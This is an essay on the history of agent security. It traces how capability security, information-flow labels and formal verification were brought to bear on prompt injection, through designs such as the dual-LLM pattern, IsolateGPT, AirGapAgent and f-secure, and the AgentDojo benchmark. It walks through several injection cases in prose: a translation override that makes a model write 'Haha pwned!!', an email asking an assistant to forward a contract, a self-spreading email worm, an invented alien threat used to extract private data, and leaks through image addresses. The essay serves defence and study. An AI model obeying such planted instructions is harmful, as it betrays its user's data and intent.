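# How programming-languages and security researchers entered AI agent safety, and what they changed

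## AI agents, prompt injection and the older security ideas

An AI agent is a program in which a large language model chooses actions and carries them out through tools. Unlike a chatbot, which only returns text to the user, an agent can read files, search the web, send email or pay an invoice. People find agents useful largely because they do these things without someone approving every step. That also makes agents a security problem, since anyone who can get text into the model's input may be able to influence what the agent does.

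From about 2023, researchers from three older fields of computer science began working on that problem. Capability security concerns how programs get permissions. Language-based security tracks where data goes inside a program. Formal methods use mathematics to check that a program does what its designers specified. Most of the ideas these researchers brought date from between 1966 and 1988, when many users shared one large computer and had good reason to distrust each other's programs.

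### How an agent works, and how an email can hijack it

The model only takes in text and produces text, so ordinary software around it, called the harness, has to carry out actions such as sending an email. The harness combines the developer's standing instructions, descriptions of the available tools and the user's request into one long text. The model responds with either an answer or a tool call, which is a structured request to run a function, such as `send_email` with an address, a subject and a body. The harness runs the function or refuses to, adds the result to the end of the text and passes all of it back to the model. This repeats until the model produces a final answer.

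Many harnesses find their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard that Anthropic, the company behind the Claude models, published in November 2024. A service that offers tools over MCP supplies each tool's name, a plain-language description and the arguments it takes, and the harness copies these into the model's input. This makes it easy to connect an agent to a new service, but it also lets whoever runs the service write some of what the model reads.

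Suppose a user asks an assistant to go through the morning's email and answer anything routine. The assistant has tools to read mail, search the user's files and send mail. Below some ordinary text about a delivery, one message from a stranger tells AI assistants to find the latest contract in the user's files and forward it to an outside address. Once the harness has fetched that message, the model's input contains instructions from both the user and the stranger. The attack works if the model follows the stranger's instructions. This is called prompt injection, in which text planted in data an agent reads makes the agent act against its user's wishes.

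In *SPA*, a design for safer agents from the University of South Florida, Girrens and Wang (2026) say the root of prompt injection is that instructions and data share the same natural-language channel. Databases once had a similar weakness. Attackers typed database commands into web forms, and careless programs pasted that text into their own commands. Programmers fixed this by sending the command and the data separately, so that the database never treats the data as a command. A language model has no separate input for data. A harness can put markers around the email to show that it is data, and training can make a model more likely to treat it that way, but can't guarantee it.

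An attack doesn't need to contain an instruction. Girrens and Wang describe an invoice that carries an attacker's bank account number. The agent can do exactly what its user asked, in the right order, and still pay the wrong person. This can also happen a day later, if the user has the agent save the invoice on Monday and on Tuesday asks it to pay the invoice they discussed the day before. Even a very good filter for suspicious commands would miss attacks like this. A malicious service can also write a tool description that steers the model before any tool has run.

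### A checkpoint outside the model

In 1972 the US Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972) reported a specialist panel's assessment of this idea. Most defences at the time put a barrier around the machine and trusted everyone inside it. The panel worried about a malicious user with a legitimate account, who could write and run any program he liked. A hostile email is in a fairly similar position, since it is already part of the text the agent is processing when the attack begins.

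The panel recommended a reference monitor, a trusted component that checks every request against a policy before it takes effect. The policy can be a table with users and programs as rows, files and devices as columns, and the permitted actions in the cells. Anderson requires the checking mechanism to be tamper-proof, to handle every request, and to be small enough for people to analyse and test completely. Commercial systems of the time fell well short. Much of Honeywell's GCOS III operating system ran with the memory checks suspended, and with its supporting software it had between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions, far too many to analyse.

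Anderson also harshly criticizes testing a system by hiring people to break into it. These "tiger teams" had so far succeeded every time, but he argues that even if one had failed, the system's security would still have been unknown.

In an agent, the harness is the natural place for a reference monitor, because tool calls already have to pass through it. The model is a poor place for one. For example, a developer's instruction to ignore commands in emails fails all of Anderson's requirements, because an attacker can try to get the model to disregard it, the model may not apply it every time, and nobody can analyse billions of learned parameters the way an engineer analyses a few thousand lines of code. The instruction probably still stops some attacks, but it isn't a substitute for a check in the harness.

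Saltzer and Schroeder (1975), in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, drew eight design principles from the experience of that period. The best known is least privilege: every program and user should have only the permissions the job needs, so that an accident or an attack does less damage. Complete mediation requires a check on every access to every object. Under fail-safe defaults, the system refuses anything that nobody has explicitly allowed. This makes mistakes easier to catch, because a user who is wrongly refused access soon complains, while a missing prohibition may go unnoticed until an attacker finds it.

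The other principles call for a simple design, a design that doesn't depend on secrecy, two keys instead of one where feasible, little machinery shared between users, and an interface that people will use correctly without thinking about it. The last, which Saltzer and Schroeder call psychological acceptability, matters a lot for agents. If a harness requires its user to approve forty emails a day, the user will soon click yes without reading them.

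A reference monitor in the harness still cannot detect whether a call to `send_email` resulted from the user's request or the stranger's text. The policy has to allow the call because sending mail is part of the assistant's job.

### Capabilities and the confused deputy

Tymshare, a company that rented out time on shared computers, ran into a version of this problem in the 1970s, as Norm Hardy recounted in *The Confused Deputy* (1988). Tymshare kept a compiler, a program that translates source code into machine code, in a directory called SYSX. The compiler collected statistics on which language features people used and wrote them to a file in the same directory, so its operators had given it permission to write files there. Customers could also name a file for the compiler's debugging output. One customer learned that SYSX also held the company's billing records, in a file called BILL, and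 named that file. The operating system let the compiler open it because the compiler had permission to write in SYSX, and the billing records were lost.

It isn't obvious what anyone should have done differently. The compiler's developers couldn't have made it reject file names in SYSX, because the directory didn't have that name when they wrote the code, and someone with proper access might want to send output there. Checking only for BILL would have left the other sensitive files exposed. Tymshare then added a way for a program to switch between its own authority and its customer's, but some programs soon needed more than two authorities. When Hardy last wrote down the full rule for when a program could open a file, it contained fourteen "ands" and "ors".

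According to Hardy, the compiler had authority from two sources and no way to keep them apart. The customer supplied the file's name but not the permission to write to it. Hardy calls a program a confused deputy when it has legitimate authority and someone tricks it into using that authority for them. The mail assistant fits this description well, because the stranger supplies an address and the user's account supplies the permission to send.

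The remedy he proposed was already more than twenty years old. Dennis and Van Horn, two researchers at MIT, had set it out in *Programming Semantics for Multiprogrammed Computations* (1966), which they first presented at a conference on programming languages. In their scheme, every computation has a list of capabilities. Each one points to an object, such as a segment of memory, and specifies whether the computation may read it, write to it or execute it as code. The program refers to the object by the capability's position in the list, and it cannot refer to anything that isn't on the list.

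With capabilities, Tymshare's compiler would have held a capability for the statistics file, and each customer would have passed it another for the debugging output. A customer without access to BILL couldn't have passed a capability for it. The compiler wouldn't have needed file names, and nobody would have needed the rule with the fourteen "ands" and "ors".

On most computers, including those running Unix, a program asks to open a file by name, and the system checks whose account the program runs under. *Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro, 2003) calls this ambient authority, meaning authority that a program uses without selecting it. The paper compares it to a world of doors without keys, where a door opens if the person in front of it is allowed through. A program with ambient authority gets its permissions from the user who runs it, and nobody has to grant them for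 the specific task.

Miller and Shapiro illustrate the difference in *Paradigm Regained* with two Unix commands that copy a file, `cp foo.txt bar.txt` and `cat < foo.txt > bar.txt`. The `cp` program receives two file names, and it needs permission to open all the user's files because the user might name any of them. In the second command, the user's shell (the program that interprets typed commands) opens both files first and passes `cat` two open connections. The `cat` program needs only those connections, but Unix still runs it with the user's full authority. A game of Solitaire also runs with that authority, so it could read the user's email and sell parts of it online without breaking any of the system's rules.

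Mark Miller and others carried the idea over from operating systems to programming languages. An object capability is an unforgeable reference that both names an object and grants the right to use it. Code can affect only the objects it has references to. It may have a reference from the start, create the object itself, or receive the reference from code that already has one. Miller states this rule in his doctoral thesis, *Robust Composition* (2006), as "only connectivity begets connectivity". The language has to block every other way of getting access to an object. C++ fails, as Miller and Shapiro point out, because a programmer can turn a number into a pointer to any place in memory, and Java fails because it has global variables that any code can change.

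References can also be temporary. Miller and colleagues describe a small forwarding object that stands between a program and a resource. The program uses the forwarder as if it were the resource. When the owner disables the forwarder, the program loses access, and so does anyone the program had shared the forwarder with.

A capability design for the mail assistant would drop the general `send_email` function, which accepts any address. The harness would instead give the model an object that can do only one thing, such as reply in a particular thread, and would revoke that object when the task ends. The model would then have no means of writing to any outside addresses mentioned in the stranger's email.

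This limits the damage a lot, but it is not a complete defence. Suppose the user asked for replies to routine mail, and the stranger's message looks routine. The model then has capabilities to reply to the stranger and to read the user's files, and nothing stops it from using both to put the contract in the reply. Hardy could assume that the compiler's code was correct, but in an agent, the attacker's text influences the part of the program that decides which capability to use for what purpose.

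Before AI agents, capability security was mostly the work of a small, close community. In his thesis, Miller presents the language E and the desktop system CapDesk, and thanks two online groups, e-lang and cap-talk, along with Hewlett-Packard Laboratories and the US defence research agency DARPA. Google Research's list of his publications, *Mark S. Miller*, includes papers at a USENIX security workshop and a symposium on dynamic languages. Large companies also tried the idea. *Objects as Secure Capabilities* (Duffy, 2015) describes Midori, an experimental Microsoft operating system whose team included designers of earlier capability systems.

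Little of this reached ordinary computers under its own name. Miller and colleagues count Unix file descriptors, the open connections in the `cat` example, as nearly but not quite object capabilities. Linux and Android have a feature called "capabilities", but Duffy says these aren't real capabilities. Many people also mistakenly thought that capabilities and lists of permitted users were two ways to write down the same table. Miller and colleagues write in a footnote that the security researcher David Wagner believed roughly this until one of them convinced him otherwise. The blog Habitat Chronicles (2017) attributed some of the resistance to engineers' healthy wariness of novelty and some to "academic tribalism".

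### Labels that follow the data

Capabilities control what a program can reach. To keep the contract out of the reply, the harness must also track where the reply's text came from. Information-flow control does this by labeling data, and it restricts where the data and anything derived from it may go.

The standard theory comes from Denning's *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (1976). Every piece of data belongs to a security class, and A → B means that information in class A may flow into class B. When a program combines data from two classes, the result belongs to their join, written A ⊕ B, the lowest class that both can flow into. Denning argues that this follows from what information flow means. If a program computes c := a + b and b is zero, then c is a copy of a, so any class that may receive the sum must also be allowed to receive a on its own. With a few mild assumptions,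 such as a finite number of classes, the classes form a lattice, an ordered set in which any two members have a unique join.

Four classes are enough for the mail assistant. Each combines a confidentiality label, Public or Secret, which records who may read the data, with an integrity label, Trusted or Untrusted, which records whether anyone should rely on it. Data may flow from Public to Secret and from Trusted to Untrusted, but not in the reverse direction.

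| Data | Confidentiality | Integrity |
|---|---|---|
| The user's request | Public | Trusted |
| The contract | Secret | Trusted |
| The stranger's email | Public | Untrusted |
| A reply that draws on the contract and the email | Secret | Untrusted |

The user's request is at the bottom of the lattice, so it can flow anywhere. The contract and the email are side by side in the middle, and neither can flow to the other's class. The last row comes from the join rule, which takes the more restrictive value in each column:

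(Secret, Trusted) ⊕ (Public, Untrusted) = (Secret, Untrusted)

The harness can now check a call to `send_email`. An outsider will read the body, so it has to be Public. The address decides where the information goes, so it has to be Trusted. If the model tries to forward the contract to the address in the stranger's email, the call fails both checks, because the body is Secret and the address is not Trusted. If the model puts the contract in a reply to the stranger, the call fails only because the body is Secret. Capabilities alone would allow that reply.

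Copying is the easy case, but Denning pointed out that information also moves through a program's conditional statements, such as `if a = 0 then b := 0`. If b starts out as 1, anyone who can see b afterwards knows whether a was zero, although the program never copied a into b. She calls this an implicit flow. It happens even when the assignment doesn't run, because if b is still 1, a wasn't zero. The stranger could use the same trick by asking for a reply that says only "thanks" if the contract is worth more than a million dollars, and for no reply otherwise.

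One way to catch this is to label the program's current position as well as its data. Denning describes a design by the computer scientist Fenton that works this way. When the machine enters a branch, it joins the label of the condition to the label of the current position, and it restores the old label when it leaves. Anything the program writes inside the branch must satisfy both labels. A language model has no visible branches, and any part of the text it reads may affect any part of its output, so the cautious assumption is that everything it has read influences every later call. Once the model has read the stranger's email, even its harmless calls count as untrusted, which is a version of the old problem of label creep.

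Researchers later stated the goal of all this in one line. Let P be a program, and let s ~ t mean that two starting states s and t contain the same Public data, though their Secret data may differ. Then P satisfies noninterference if, for all s and t,

s ~ t implies P(s) ~ P(t).

In words, changing the secrets doesn't change anything the public can see. (This simple version ignores how long the program takes and whether it finishes.) For integrity, ~ means that the two states contain the same Trusted data. If two inboxes differ only in the wording of the stranger's email, then under noninterference the assistant can summarise the two emails differently, because the summaries are Untrusted, but it has to send its mail to the same addresses in both cases.

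Hardly any useful program satisfies this all the time. A user may want the assistant to send the contract to the buyer, which means deliberately lowering the contract's confidentiality label. This is called declassification. Deliberately raising an integrity label, for instance after the user has confirmed a bank account number, is called endorsement. Even an ordinary reply needs an endorsement, because the sender's address arrived in an untrusted email. Much of the difficulty lies in these exceptions, because the labels achieve very little if the stranger's text can influence what the user declassifies.

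Girrens and Wang's measurements show how much an agent depends on endorsement. With their information-flow checks on, their agent's success rate fell from 53.0% to 29.0% on AgentDojo, a benchmark that measures how well agents complete tasks and resist prompt injection. The rate fell mainly because the checks rejected plans that used outside data in sensitive actions, and much legitimate work requires such plans, like paying an invoice that came by email.

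Work on information flow appeared in operating-systems and security venues and later at programming-language conferences. Denning presented a version of her model at the ACM's operating-systems symposium in 1975. The military was the obvious customer because it already put classification labels on paper documents. Sandhu still introduced the subject mainly through military and government labels in *Lattice-Based Access Control Models* (1993). Programming languages with full label checking, such as Jif, an extension of Java, stayed mostly in universities. Ordinary programmers were more likely to meet simpler related features, such as Perl's "taint mode", which marks outside input and blocks its use in certain risky operations until the program has checked it.

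### What a proof covers

Formal methods need a specification, which is a precise statement of what a program must or must never do, and a checker, which is a program that decides whether another program meets the specification. Some checkers work on their own, while others confirm each step of a proof written by a person or another program.

Denning and Denning (1977), in *Certification of Programs for Secure Information Flow*, built an early checker for labels. The programmer declares a security class next to each variable's type, and the compiler checks every assignment, branch and loop before the program runs. Checking the whole text also covers branches that would be missed by watching a particular run. They proved that the compiler certifies a program only if it is secure.

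Denning and Denning showed that no procedure can decide exactly which programs are secure, since it would also have to decide whether an arbitrary computation ever stops, which is impossible. So their compiler, like many checkers, rejects some safe programs so that it never accepts an unsafe one. For example, it rejects `if x = 0 then if x ≠ 0 then y := z` when z is not allowed to flow to y, although the assignment never runs because x can't be both zero and non-zero.

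A proof also has limits. Denning and Denning say that theirs does not cover hardware faults or covert channels, which are ways to pass information outside the program's stored data, for instance by slowing the machine down in a pattern. Anderson requires both a proof that the model of a system is secure and a demonstration that the real system matches the model. In 2009 a team in Australia finished a machine-checked proof that the roughly 8,700 lines of C code in seL4, an operating-system kernel built on capabilities, met their specification. That proof still depended on the hardware and the compiler working correctly.

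With agents, the specification is probably the weakest point. For example, a harness might let an assistant write only to people in the user's address book. A proof that the harness enforces this rule holds whatever the model outputs and however clever a stranger's email is. Testing the model can't provide that guarantee. But the assistant can still send a contract to the wrong colleague without breaking the rule. Saltzer and Schroeder had warned that people who look only at the protection mechanisms, especially ones that no attacker could beat even in principle, can end up trusting the rest of the system too much.

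Types are the kind of specification most programmers already use. A type such as `Email → Summary` specifies that a function takes an email and returns a summary, and the compiler rejects code that doesn't match. In most languages, the function could still delete a file along the way. Some languages also track effects, meaning anything a function does besides returning a result. In Haskell, the type of a function that sends mail has to show that it interacts with the outside world, so the compiler would reject an `Email → Summary` function that sends mail. A more detailed effect system can distinguish reading a file from sending a message.

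In the mail assistant, a programmer can therefore handle the stranger's email in code that has no way to send anything, and have the compiler confirm that it can't. The dual-LLM pattern divides the work similarly, by having a model without tools read the untrusted text. The guarantee holds only if the language has no way around the compiler's check, or if programmers are banned from using it (Haskell has one, called `unsafePerformIO`). It also covers only what the code does, so the summary it returns may still be false or contain the stranger's instructions word for word.

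Before agents, types were the only part of formal methods used in nearly all ordinary software. Full proofs were rare and expensive, and were mostly done for small, critical pieces of code. The research appeared at conferences on programming languages and automated verification, and by the 2010s some of it had begun to incorporate the other two traditions. In *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks* (2016), Rajani, Garg and Rezk proved that access control and object capabilities are fundamentally different. They also gave the first formal definition, in a programming-language setting, of freedom from confused-deputy attacks, and related it to integrity in information flow. *Robust and Compositional Verification of Object Capability Patterns* (2017) presented a logic for proving that an object's private state stays safe when its program runs alongside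 unknown and untrusted code.

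## 2022 to 2024: the first attempts to borrow from security research

In September 2022 Riley Goodside posted examples on Twitter in which he asked GPT-3, then OpenAI's main language model, to translate a sentence into French. The sentence contained an instruction to ignore the translation directions and write "Haha pwned!!" instead, and GPT-3 did. The next day Simon Willison (2022), a programmer who had co-created the web framework Django, proposed the name "prompt injection" for this kind of attack in *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3*.

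Willison was thinking of SQL injection, an attack on databases through web forms, and he hoped developers could fix prompt injection the same way, by passing instructions and data to the model separately. A reader pointed out that one of OpenAI's models already accepted them separately and was still vulnerable to attacks hidden in the data. By April 2023, Willison had added a note that the fix was extremely difficult, and perhaps impossible, with the models of the time.

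At first the attacker was usually the person typing. When a recruitment startup launched a Twitter bot that replied to any mention of remote work, people quickly got it to threaten the president, which was embarrassing but did little harm. Greshake, Endres and colleagues (2023), in *Not what you've signed up for*, showed that the attacker could be someone the user had never dealt with. In what they called indirect prompt injection, the attacker puts instructions in a web page, an email or a code repository and waits for someone else's assistant to read them. For example, the Bing Chat sidebar in Microsoft's Edge browser could read the page the user was on, and the team found that it also followed instructions in text the user couldn't see.

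Several of the researchers worked in computer security, at the CISPA research centre and the company sequire technology, and they described the problem in that field's terms. They argued that when a model follows instructions in plain language, having it process a retrieved page is much like running a stranger's code. They went through the usual list of cyber threats and found a version of nearly all of them, including a worm, in which an email assistant reads a malicious message and sends copies of it to the user's contacts. Most later work on agent security also assumes an attacker who plants instructions in content the model will read.

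### Why most early defences worked on the model

In his own examples, Goodside tried the obvious defence of warning GPT-3 that the text might contain tricks and that it must ignore them. GPT-3 wrote "Haha pwned!!" anyway. He then suggested putting the untrusted text inside quotation marks in JSON, a standard data format, but Brian Mastenbrook found a sentence that got around this too. Others suggested using a second model to check whether an attack had occurred. Marco Buono replied with an input that also told the checker to report that nothing had happened, and it did. A few days after naming the attack, Willison wrote that he knew how to beat SQL injection but had "no idea how to reliably beat prompt injection".

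By 2024 researchers had more careful versions of the same approach. In *StruQ*, Chen, Piet and colleagues trained a model to follow only the instructions in one marked part of its input. A Microsoft team tried "spotlighting", which changes how untrusted text looks, for instance by putting a special character between its words. At least one person working on the model already knew the older ideas. David Wagner, who co-wrote *StruQ*, had been won over on capabilities by Miller and colleagues, by their own account, and later helped design Joe-E, a version of Java with object capabilities.

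There were decent reasons to train models to resist prompt injection. If the model itself could resist attacks, users would keep every feature and developers wouldn't have to redesign the product. Prompt injection also looked like another way for a model to misbehave, and machine-learning researchers already had methods for training out bad behaviour.

Training models to resist prompt injection has helped, and it has kept improving. In *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026), Shim, Karim and colleagues cite OpenAI's report that GPT-5.6 Sol had a sixth as many prompt-injection failures as a production model from four months earlier. But the model still fails sometimes, and an attacker can keep trying. In *System-Level Defense against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* (2024), Wu, Cecchetti and Xiao also object that a defence trained into one model may not carry over to the next, and that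 nobody can analyse it formally.

### The dual-LLM pattern

Willison (2023) assumed in his next proposal, *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, that the model would stay vulnerable. He called the most dangerous kind of prompt injection a confused deputy attack, and took the definition from Wikipedia. The confused deputy concept reached AI agents through this blog post, before most of the academic work had started.

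The pattern uses two models and a controller, which is ordinary software. The privileged model takes the user's requests and can call tools. The quarantined model reads untrusted text, has no tools, and may be under an attacker's control at any time. The controller passes things between them and makes sure the privileged model never sees anything the quarantined model writes.

Suppose the user asks for a summary of the latest email. The controller passes this request to the privileged model, which outputs an instruction to fetch the email and store it as `$VAR1`. The controller does so, but reports to the privileged model only that the variable exists. The privileged model then outputs an instruction to summarize `$VAR1`. The controller replaces the name with the email's text, runs the quarantined model on it, and stores the result as `$VAR2`. The privileged model writes a reply containing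 the name `$VAR2`, and the controller fills in the summary when it displays the reply to the user. If the email contains an instruction to delete everything in the inbox, only the quarantined model reads it, and that model cannot delete anything.

Willison allowed one exception. If the quarantined model only sorts a message into a few fixed categories, the controller can check that the output is one of them and pass it on, since a word like "invoice" can't contain a new attack.

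He also called the solution "pretty bad". It makes an assistant harder to build and less pleasant to use, and a single mistake that lets untrusted text reach the privileged model makes the rest of the work useless. The user still sees what the quarantined model writes, so an attacker can make it write a message that promises a funny picture if the user pastes some scrambled text, which contains their private data, into a website. If the controller displays images, the attack doesn't need the user to paste anything. An image's address can contain the data, and the user's device sends that address when it loads the image.

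Another weakness is that an attacker can influence what the variables contain. Suppose the user wants to send a document to an address mentioned in an email. The privileged model can plan this without seeing the address, but the quarantined model has to extract it, and the attacker can influence which address it extracts. The document can then go to the wrong person even though the plan is correct. In 2025 Willison added a note crediting CaMeL, a design from Google DeepMind, with addressing a flaw in his pattern.

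Willison didn't publish any measurements, but the pattern lasted, partly because it is easy to explain. It appears in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents*, a 2025 catalogue that applies its patterns to ten example applications.

### Keeping apps and personal data apart

Academic groups had meanwhile begun to borrow from operating systems and browsers. ChatGPT had started to support outside companies' apps, and the descriptions of all the installed apps went into the same input. In *IsolateGPT*, Wu, Roesner and colleagues (2024) demonstrated the risk with two ride-hailing apps. One app's description included an instruction to add $10 to the other's fares, and the model followed it.

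IsolateGPT separates language-model apps from one another, much as browsers and phones run each site or app in its own process. Each app has its own model and memory, and a central hub routes each request to an app. Apps can communicate only through the hub, using message formats declared beforehand, and ordinary code carries the messages. When an app wants help or data from another, the hub prompts the user for permission and adds a warning if the request doesn't fit the plan the hub made before any app ran.

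The team ran 1,598 attacks, most of them from an existing benchmark called InjecAgent. Without isolation, 20.2% succeeded. With isolation, 7.6% reached a permission dialog, which always carried a warning. Whether those attacks would have succeeded depends on what users would have clicked, which the team didn't test. The isolated system scored as well on ordinary tasks as the version without isolation, and it took less than 30% longer for about three-quarters of requests.

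IsolateGPT isn't designed to stop an attack inside a single app, and its permission check has a related gap. Wu, Cecchetti and Xiao tested it under its earlier name, SecGPT, with a user who asked it to read emails about budgets and notify a manager if any budget exceeded $1,000. One email, from an attacker, asked for all the budgets. Because the task required both reading and sending mail, SecGPT treated the attacker's message as a normal part of the task, and in the researchers' account the user approved. A reference monitor has the same problem with `send_email`.

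Google researchers worked on the data instead of the apps. Bagdasarian, Kairouz and colleagues (2024), in *AirGapAgent*, consider an assistant that knows a lot about its user and has to talk to outsiders, for example to book a restaurant. The restaurant may reasonably ask about allergies but not about mental health. This idea of appropriateness comes from contextual integrity, a theory that defines privacy as information flowing in ways that fit the setting. Because almost any fact is appropriate to share in some setting, an attacker can invent one that seems to justify the disclosure. In their example, the restaurant's side claims that aliens have invaded and will attack unless the assistant answers truthfully, then asks for the user's age. The assistant concludes that protecting Earth justifies revealing it.

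Their defence applies least privilege before the conversation begins. One model, the minimiser, reads the user's task and full profile and selects only the information the task needs. A second model talks to the outsider and has access only to that selection. The outsider's messages never reach the minimiser, so a story about aliens can only get the second model to reveal information the minimiser already approved. If the outsider has a good reason to want more, the assistant has to ask the user.

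To test this, the team had Google's Gemini Ultra invent 20 people with 26 facts each, and gave agents tasks such as booking a table or preparing for a doctor's appointment. An ordinary Gemini Ultra agent protected 94% of the data it should have kept private, but only 45% after one hijacking message. With the minimiser, the figure was 97%. These results are encouraging, but the test was fairly easy. Real inboxes aren't neat lists of facts, and each conversation had only one question and one answer. The minimiser is also a language model itself, so it isn't guaranteed to pick the right facts.

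Shim and colleagues describe AirGapAgent and similar designs as coarse-grained because these designs don't follow how an agent uses private data after receiving it. Their own defence tracks data with labels. Isolation is still used as one layer among several, and a 2026 survey by Zhou and Zhang, *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents*, groups it with information-flow control.

Roesner had studied permission prompts on phones and in browsers, and Bagdasarian had worked on privacy and security in machine learning. Neither team's background was mainly in programming languages.

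### Labels reach language models

Specialists in information flow started with a narrower problem than securing agents. *Rethinking Privacy in Machine Learning Pipelines from an Information Flow Control Perspective* (Wutschitz, Köpf and colleagues, 2023) describes several employees writing a document with an AI assistant, when only some of them know about a secret project. The assistant should draw only on files that all of them may read. The Microsoft team states this requirement as noninterference, which means that changing any other file must not change the probability of any output.

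They compared several ways to build such an assistant. A single model trained on everyone's files can leak them, even with noise added during training to hide individual contributions. A separate model for each group of readers meets the requirement but becomes impractical with many users. The best approach left the private files out of training and, for each question, searched only the files the user was allowed to read. The search uses the labels to exclude all other private files, so the model never receives them and cannot leak them.

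Two authors had come from related areas of programming-languages and security research. Boris Köpf had studied how to measure the information that programs leak, and Santiago Zanella-Béguelin had worked on machine-checked proofs about cryptography.

Wu, Cecchetti and Xiao, at the University of Wisconsin–Madison, applied information-flow labels to a full agent in September 2024. Ethan Cecchetti had worked on information-flow control at Cornell with Andrew Myers, whose group created Jif, and Chaowei Xiao had studied attacks on machine learning. Their design, f-secure, resembles the dual-LLM pattern with labels added. A planning model writes one step at a time in a fixed format, naming the tool to use and its inputs. A rule-based executor runs the step, and a security monitor stores the result with an integrity label. Later steps refer to the result by a name such as `{Data_output:1}`. If the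 planner has to read the result itself, the monitor passes on only the trusted parts.

This makes f-secure more flexible than Willison's version. In the budget example, the monitor labels the two emails from colleagues as trusted and the attacker's as untrusted. The planner therefore never sees the attacker's email, but it can read the colleagues' figures, find that one is $1,024, and decide to notify the manager.

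The labels also let the researchers prove something. Let Q₁ and Q₂ be two sets of information that agree on everything trusted and may differ in any other way. For a request q and any sequence of steps π, f-secure guarantees that

Pr[π | q, Q₁] = Pr[π | q, Q₂].

This is noninterference stated in terms of probabilities, because a language model may produce different plans for the same input. The proof treats the model as a black box, so it still holds when the developer switches models. But it assumes that the tools work correctly and the labels are right.

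On InjecAgent, attacks succeeded against an ordinary agent 51.6% of the time with GPT-3.5 Turbo and 28.7% of the time with GPT-4 Turbo. No attack succeeded against f-secure with any of the four models tested. The researchers had labelled all the tool outputs as untrusted, so the planner never read any of the attacks. The test therefore mostly confirms that the system they built behaves as they had proved it would.

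With GPT-4 Turbo, f-secure did about as well as the usual agent on ordinary tool-use tasks, but with GPT-3.5 Turbo it finished 60% of one set of tasks, while the usual agent finished 80%. The checks took less than a thousandth of a second per step. These tasks weren't designed around untrusted data, so they don't show how much worse an assistant performs when its planner can't read a stranger's email.

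The proof covers the plan but not the data that passes through it. The paper acknowledges that an untrusted web page can still cause the model summarising it to refuse. By the same reasoning, a correct plan to pay "the account in `{Data_output:1}`" can still pay a thief. f-secure also has no rule about where secrets may go, because it tracks only integrity.

Label creep is a problem for every design of this kind. In *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models*, Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues (2024) looked for a safe way to relax the labels. In their example, a user asks how to install a program, and the search returns instructions from a trusted source and a page from an unknown website. Under the standard rule, the answer is untrusted even if the model would have given the same answer from the trusted source alone.

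Their method first runs the model on all the documents, C, and gets an answer y. It then looks for a less restrictive label, and takes the smaller set C′ of documents that this label allows. The new label is acceptable if

U(y | x, C) − U(y | x, C′) ≤ λ,

where x is the user's question, U measures how well the model predicts the answer from those documents, and λ is the loss the developer will tolerate. If y is nearly as likely without the untrusted page, the page probably didn't matter.

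An attacker might fool that comparison, so the method doesn't rely on it for security. The system discards the first answer, runs the model again on C′ alone, and returns the new answer with the new label. A mistake in the comparison can make the answer worse, but it can't add text from an excluded document. I think this is the cleverest idea in the early work, although it can still leak a little information.

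The search for a lower label still uses the excluded documents, so someone who can see which replies the system blocks might learn a little about those documents, much as information leaks through Denning's implicit flows.

The team tested the method on made-up personal records, news articles and agent conversations. The method found the exact label in at least 75% of cases on each dataset. In more than 85% of cases on the agent conversations, it beat the simpler method of asking the model which documents it had used. It needs extra runs of the model, though only a few when there are two labels. It can't help when the answer actually depends on untrusted text, such as when the user wants a summary of a stranger's email.

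Seven of the ten authors had also worked on the 2023 noninterference paper, and six later worked on FIDES, the agent design that Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025) presented in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*. FIDES can support these looser labels, but its authors left them out for simplicity.

### From a query language to a shared test

Another route into the field began at ETH Zurich with a programming language called LMQL. Luca Beurer-Kellner, Marc Fischer and Martin Vechev presented it in *Prompting Is Programming* (2023) at PLDI, one of the main programming-languages conferences. An LMQL program mixes prompt text with ordinary code and constraints on what the model may write, such as requiring an answer to come from a given list. As the model generates text, the system rules out any next word that would break a constraint.

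LMQL was meant to make prompting more reliable and cheaper, not to provide security. But it could enforce the kind of fixed output that Willison's exception needs, and it treated the model as one component in a program whose other parts follow definite rules. Beurer-Kellner, Fischer and Vechev soon applied that view to agents. *AI Agents with Formal Security Guarantees* (2024), which they wrote with Mislav Balunović, proposed an analyser that checks an agent's actions against a written security policy. Siddiqui and colleagues cite this among the earlier uses of information-flow tracking with language models.

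The group also started a company, Invariant Labs, which built tools to check agents' tool calls against rules and scan MCP services for malicious tool descriptions. Snyk, which sells security software to developers, announced in June 2025 that it had acquired the company. Of the early academic efforts, this one led most directly to a commercial product, though the acquisition doesn't show that the tools prevented attacks.

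Invariant's researchers probably had more influence through AgentDojo, which they built with Edoardo Debenedetti, Jie Zhang and Florian Tramèr of ETH Zurich and published in June 2024. The results of the early designs are hard to compare because each group ran its own test. The IsolateGPT team extended the InjecAgent benchmark and counted permission dialogs. Wu, Cecchetti and Xiao used the same benchmark with simulated tool outputs, while Bagdasarian and colleagues tested with users they invented.

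AgentDojo has four simulated settings: an office workspace, a Slack-style chat system, a bank and a travel agency. Together they have 74 tools and 97 user tasks, such as paying a bill or finding a free slot in a calendar. Each setting also has a list of attacker goals, such as sending money to the attacker's account. The benchmark pairs every user task with every attacker goal in the same setting, so the workspace's 40 tasks and six goals give 240 test cases, and all four settings give 629. Each test case places the attack in data the agent will read during the task, such as the body of an email. A typical attack is text written to look like an important message from the user, with instructions to do something else first.

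Ordinary code then inspects the simulated accounts and inboxes to see what the agent did. AgentDojo reports three numbers from these checks. Benign utility is the share of user tasks the agent completes when there is no attack. Utility under attack is the share of test cases in which it completes the user's task without doing anything the attacker wanted. The attack success rate is the share in which the agent achieves the attacker's goal. Researchers need all three because an agent that refuses every request has an attack success rate of zero but completes no user tasks.

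This opened the field to people who had never trained a model. They could replace the whole agent with their own design, perhaps one built around an interpreter or a type system, keep the tasks, tools and scoring, and report results that machine-learning researchers would recognise. The scores also showed how much a strict design reduced the agent's ability to complete tasks, which a security proof does not measure.

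AgentDojo has the weakness that Anderson saw in tiger teams, because a defence that blocks all 629 attacks could still fail against a new one. The designers expected this and made it easy to add attacks and defences. Others have since built more open-ended tests, such as AgentDyn, cited in *Architecting Secure AI Agents* (2026), but researchers were still reporting AgentDojo scores in 2026. Debenedetti and Tramèr themselves used AgentDojo to evaluate CaMeL, which they developed with colleagues at Google.

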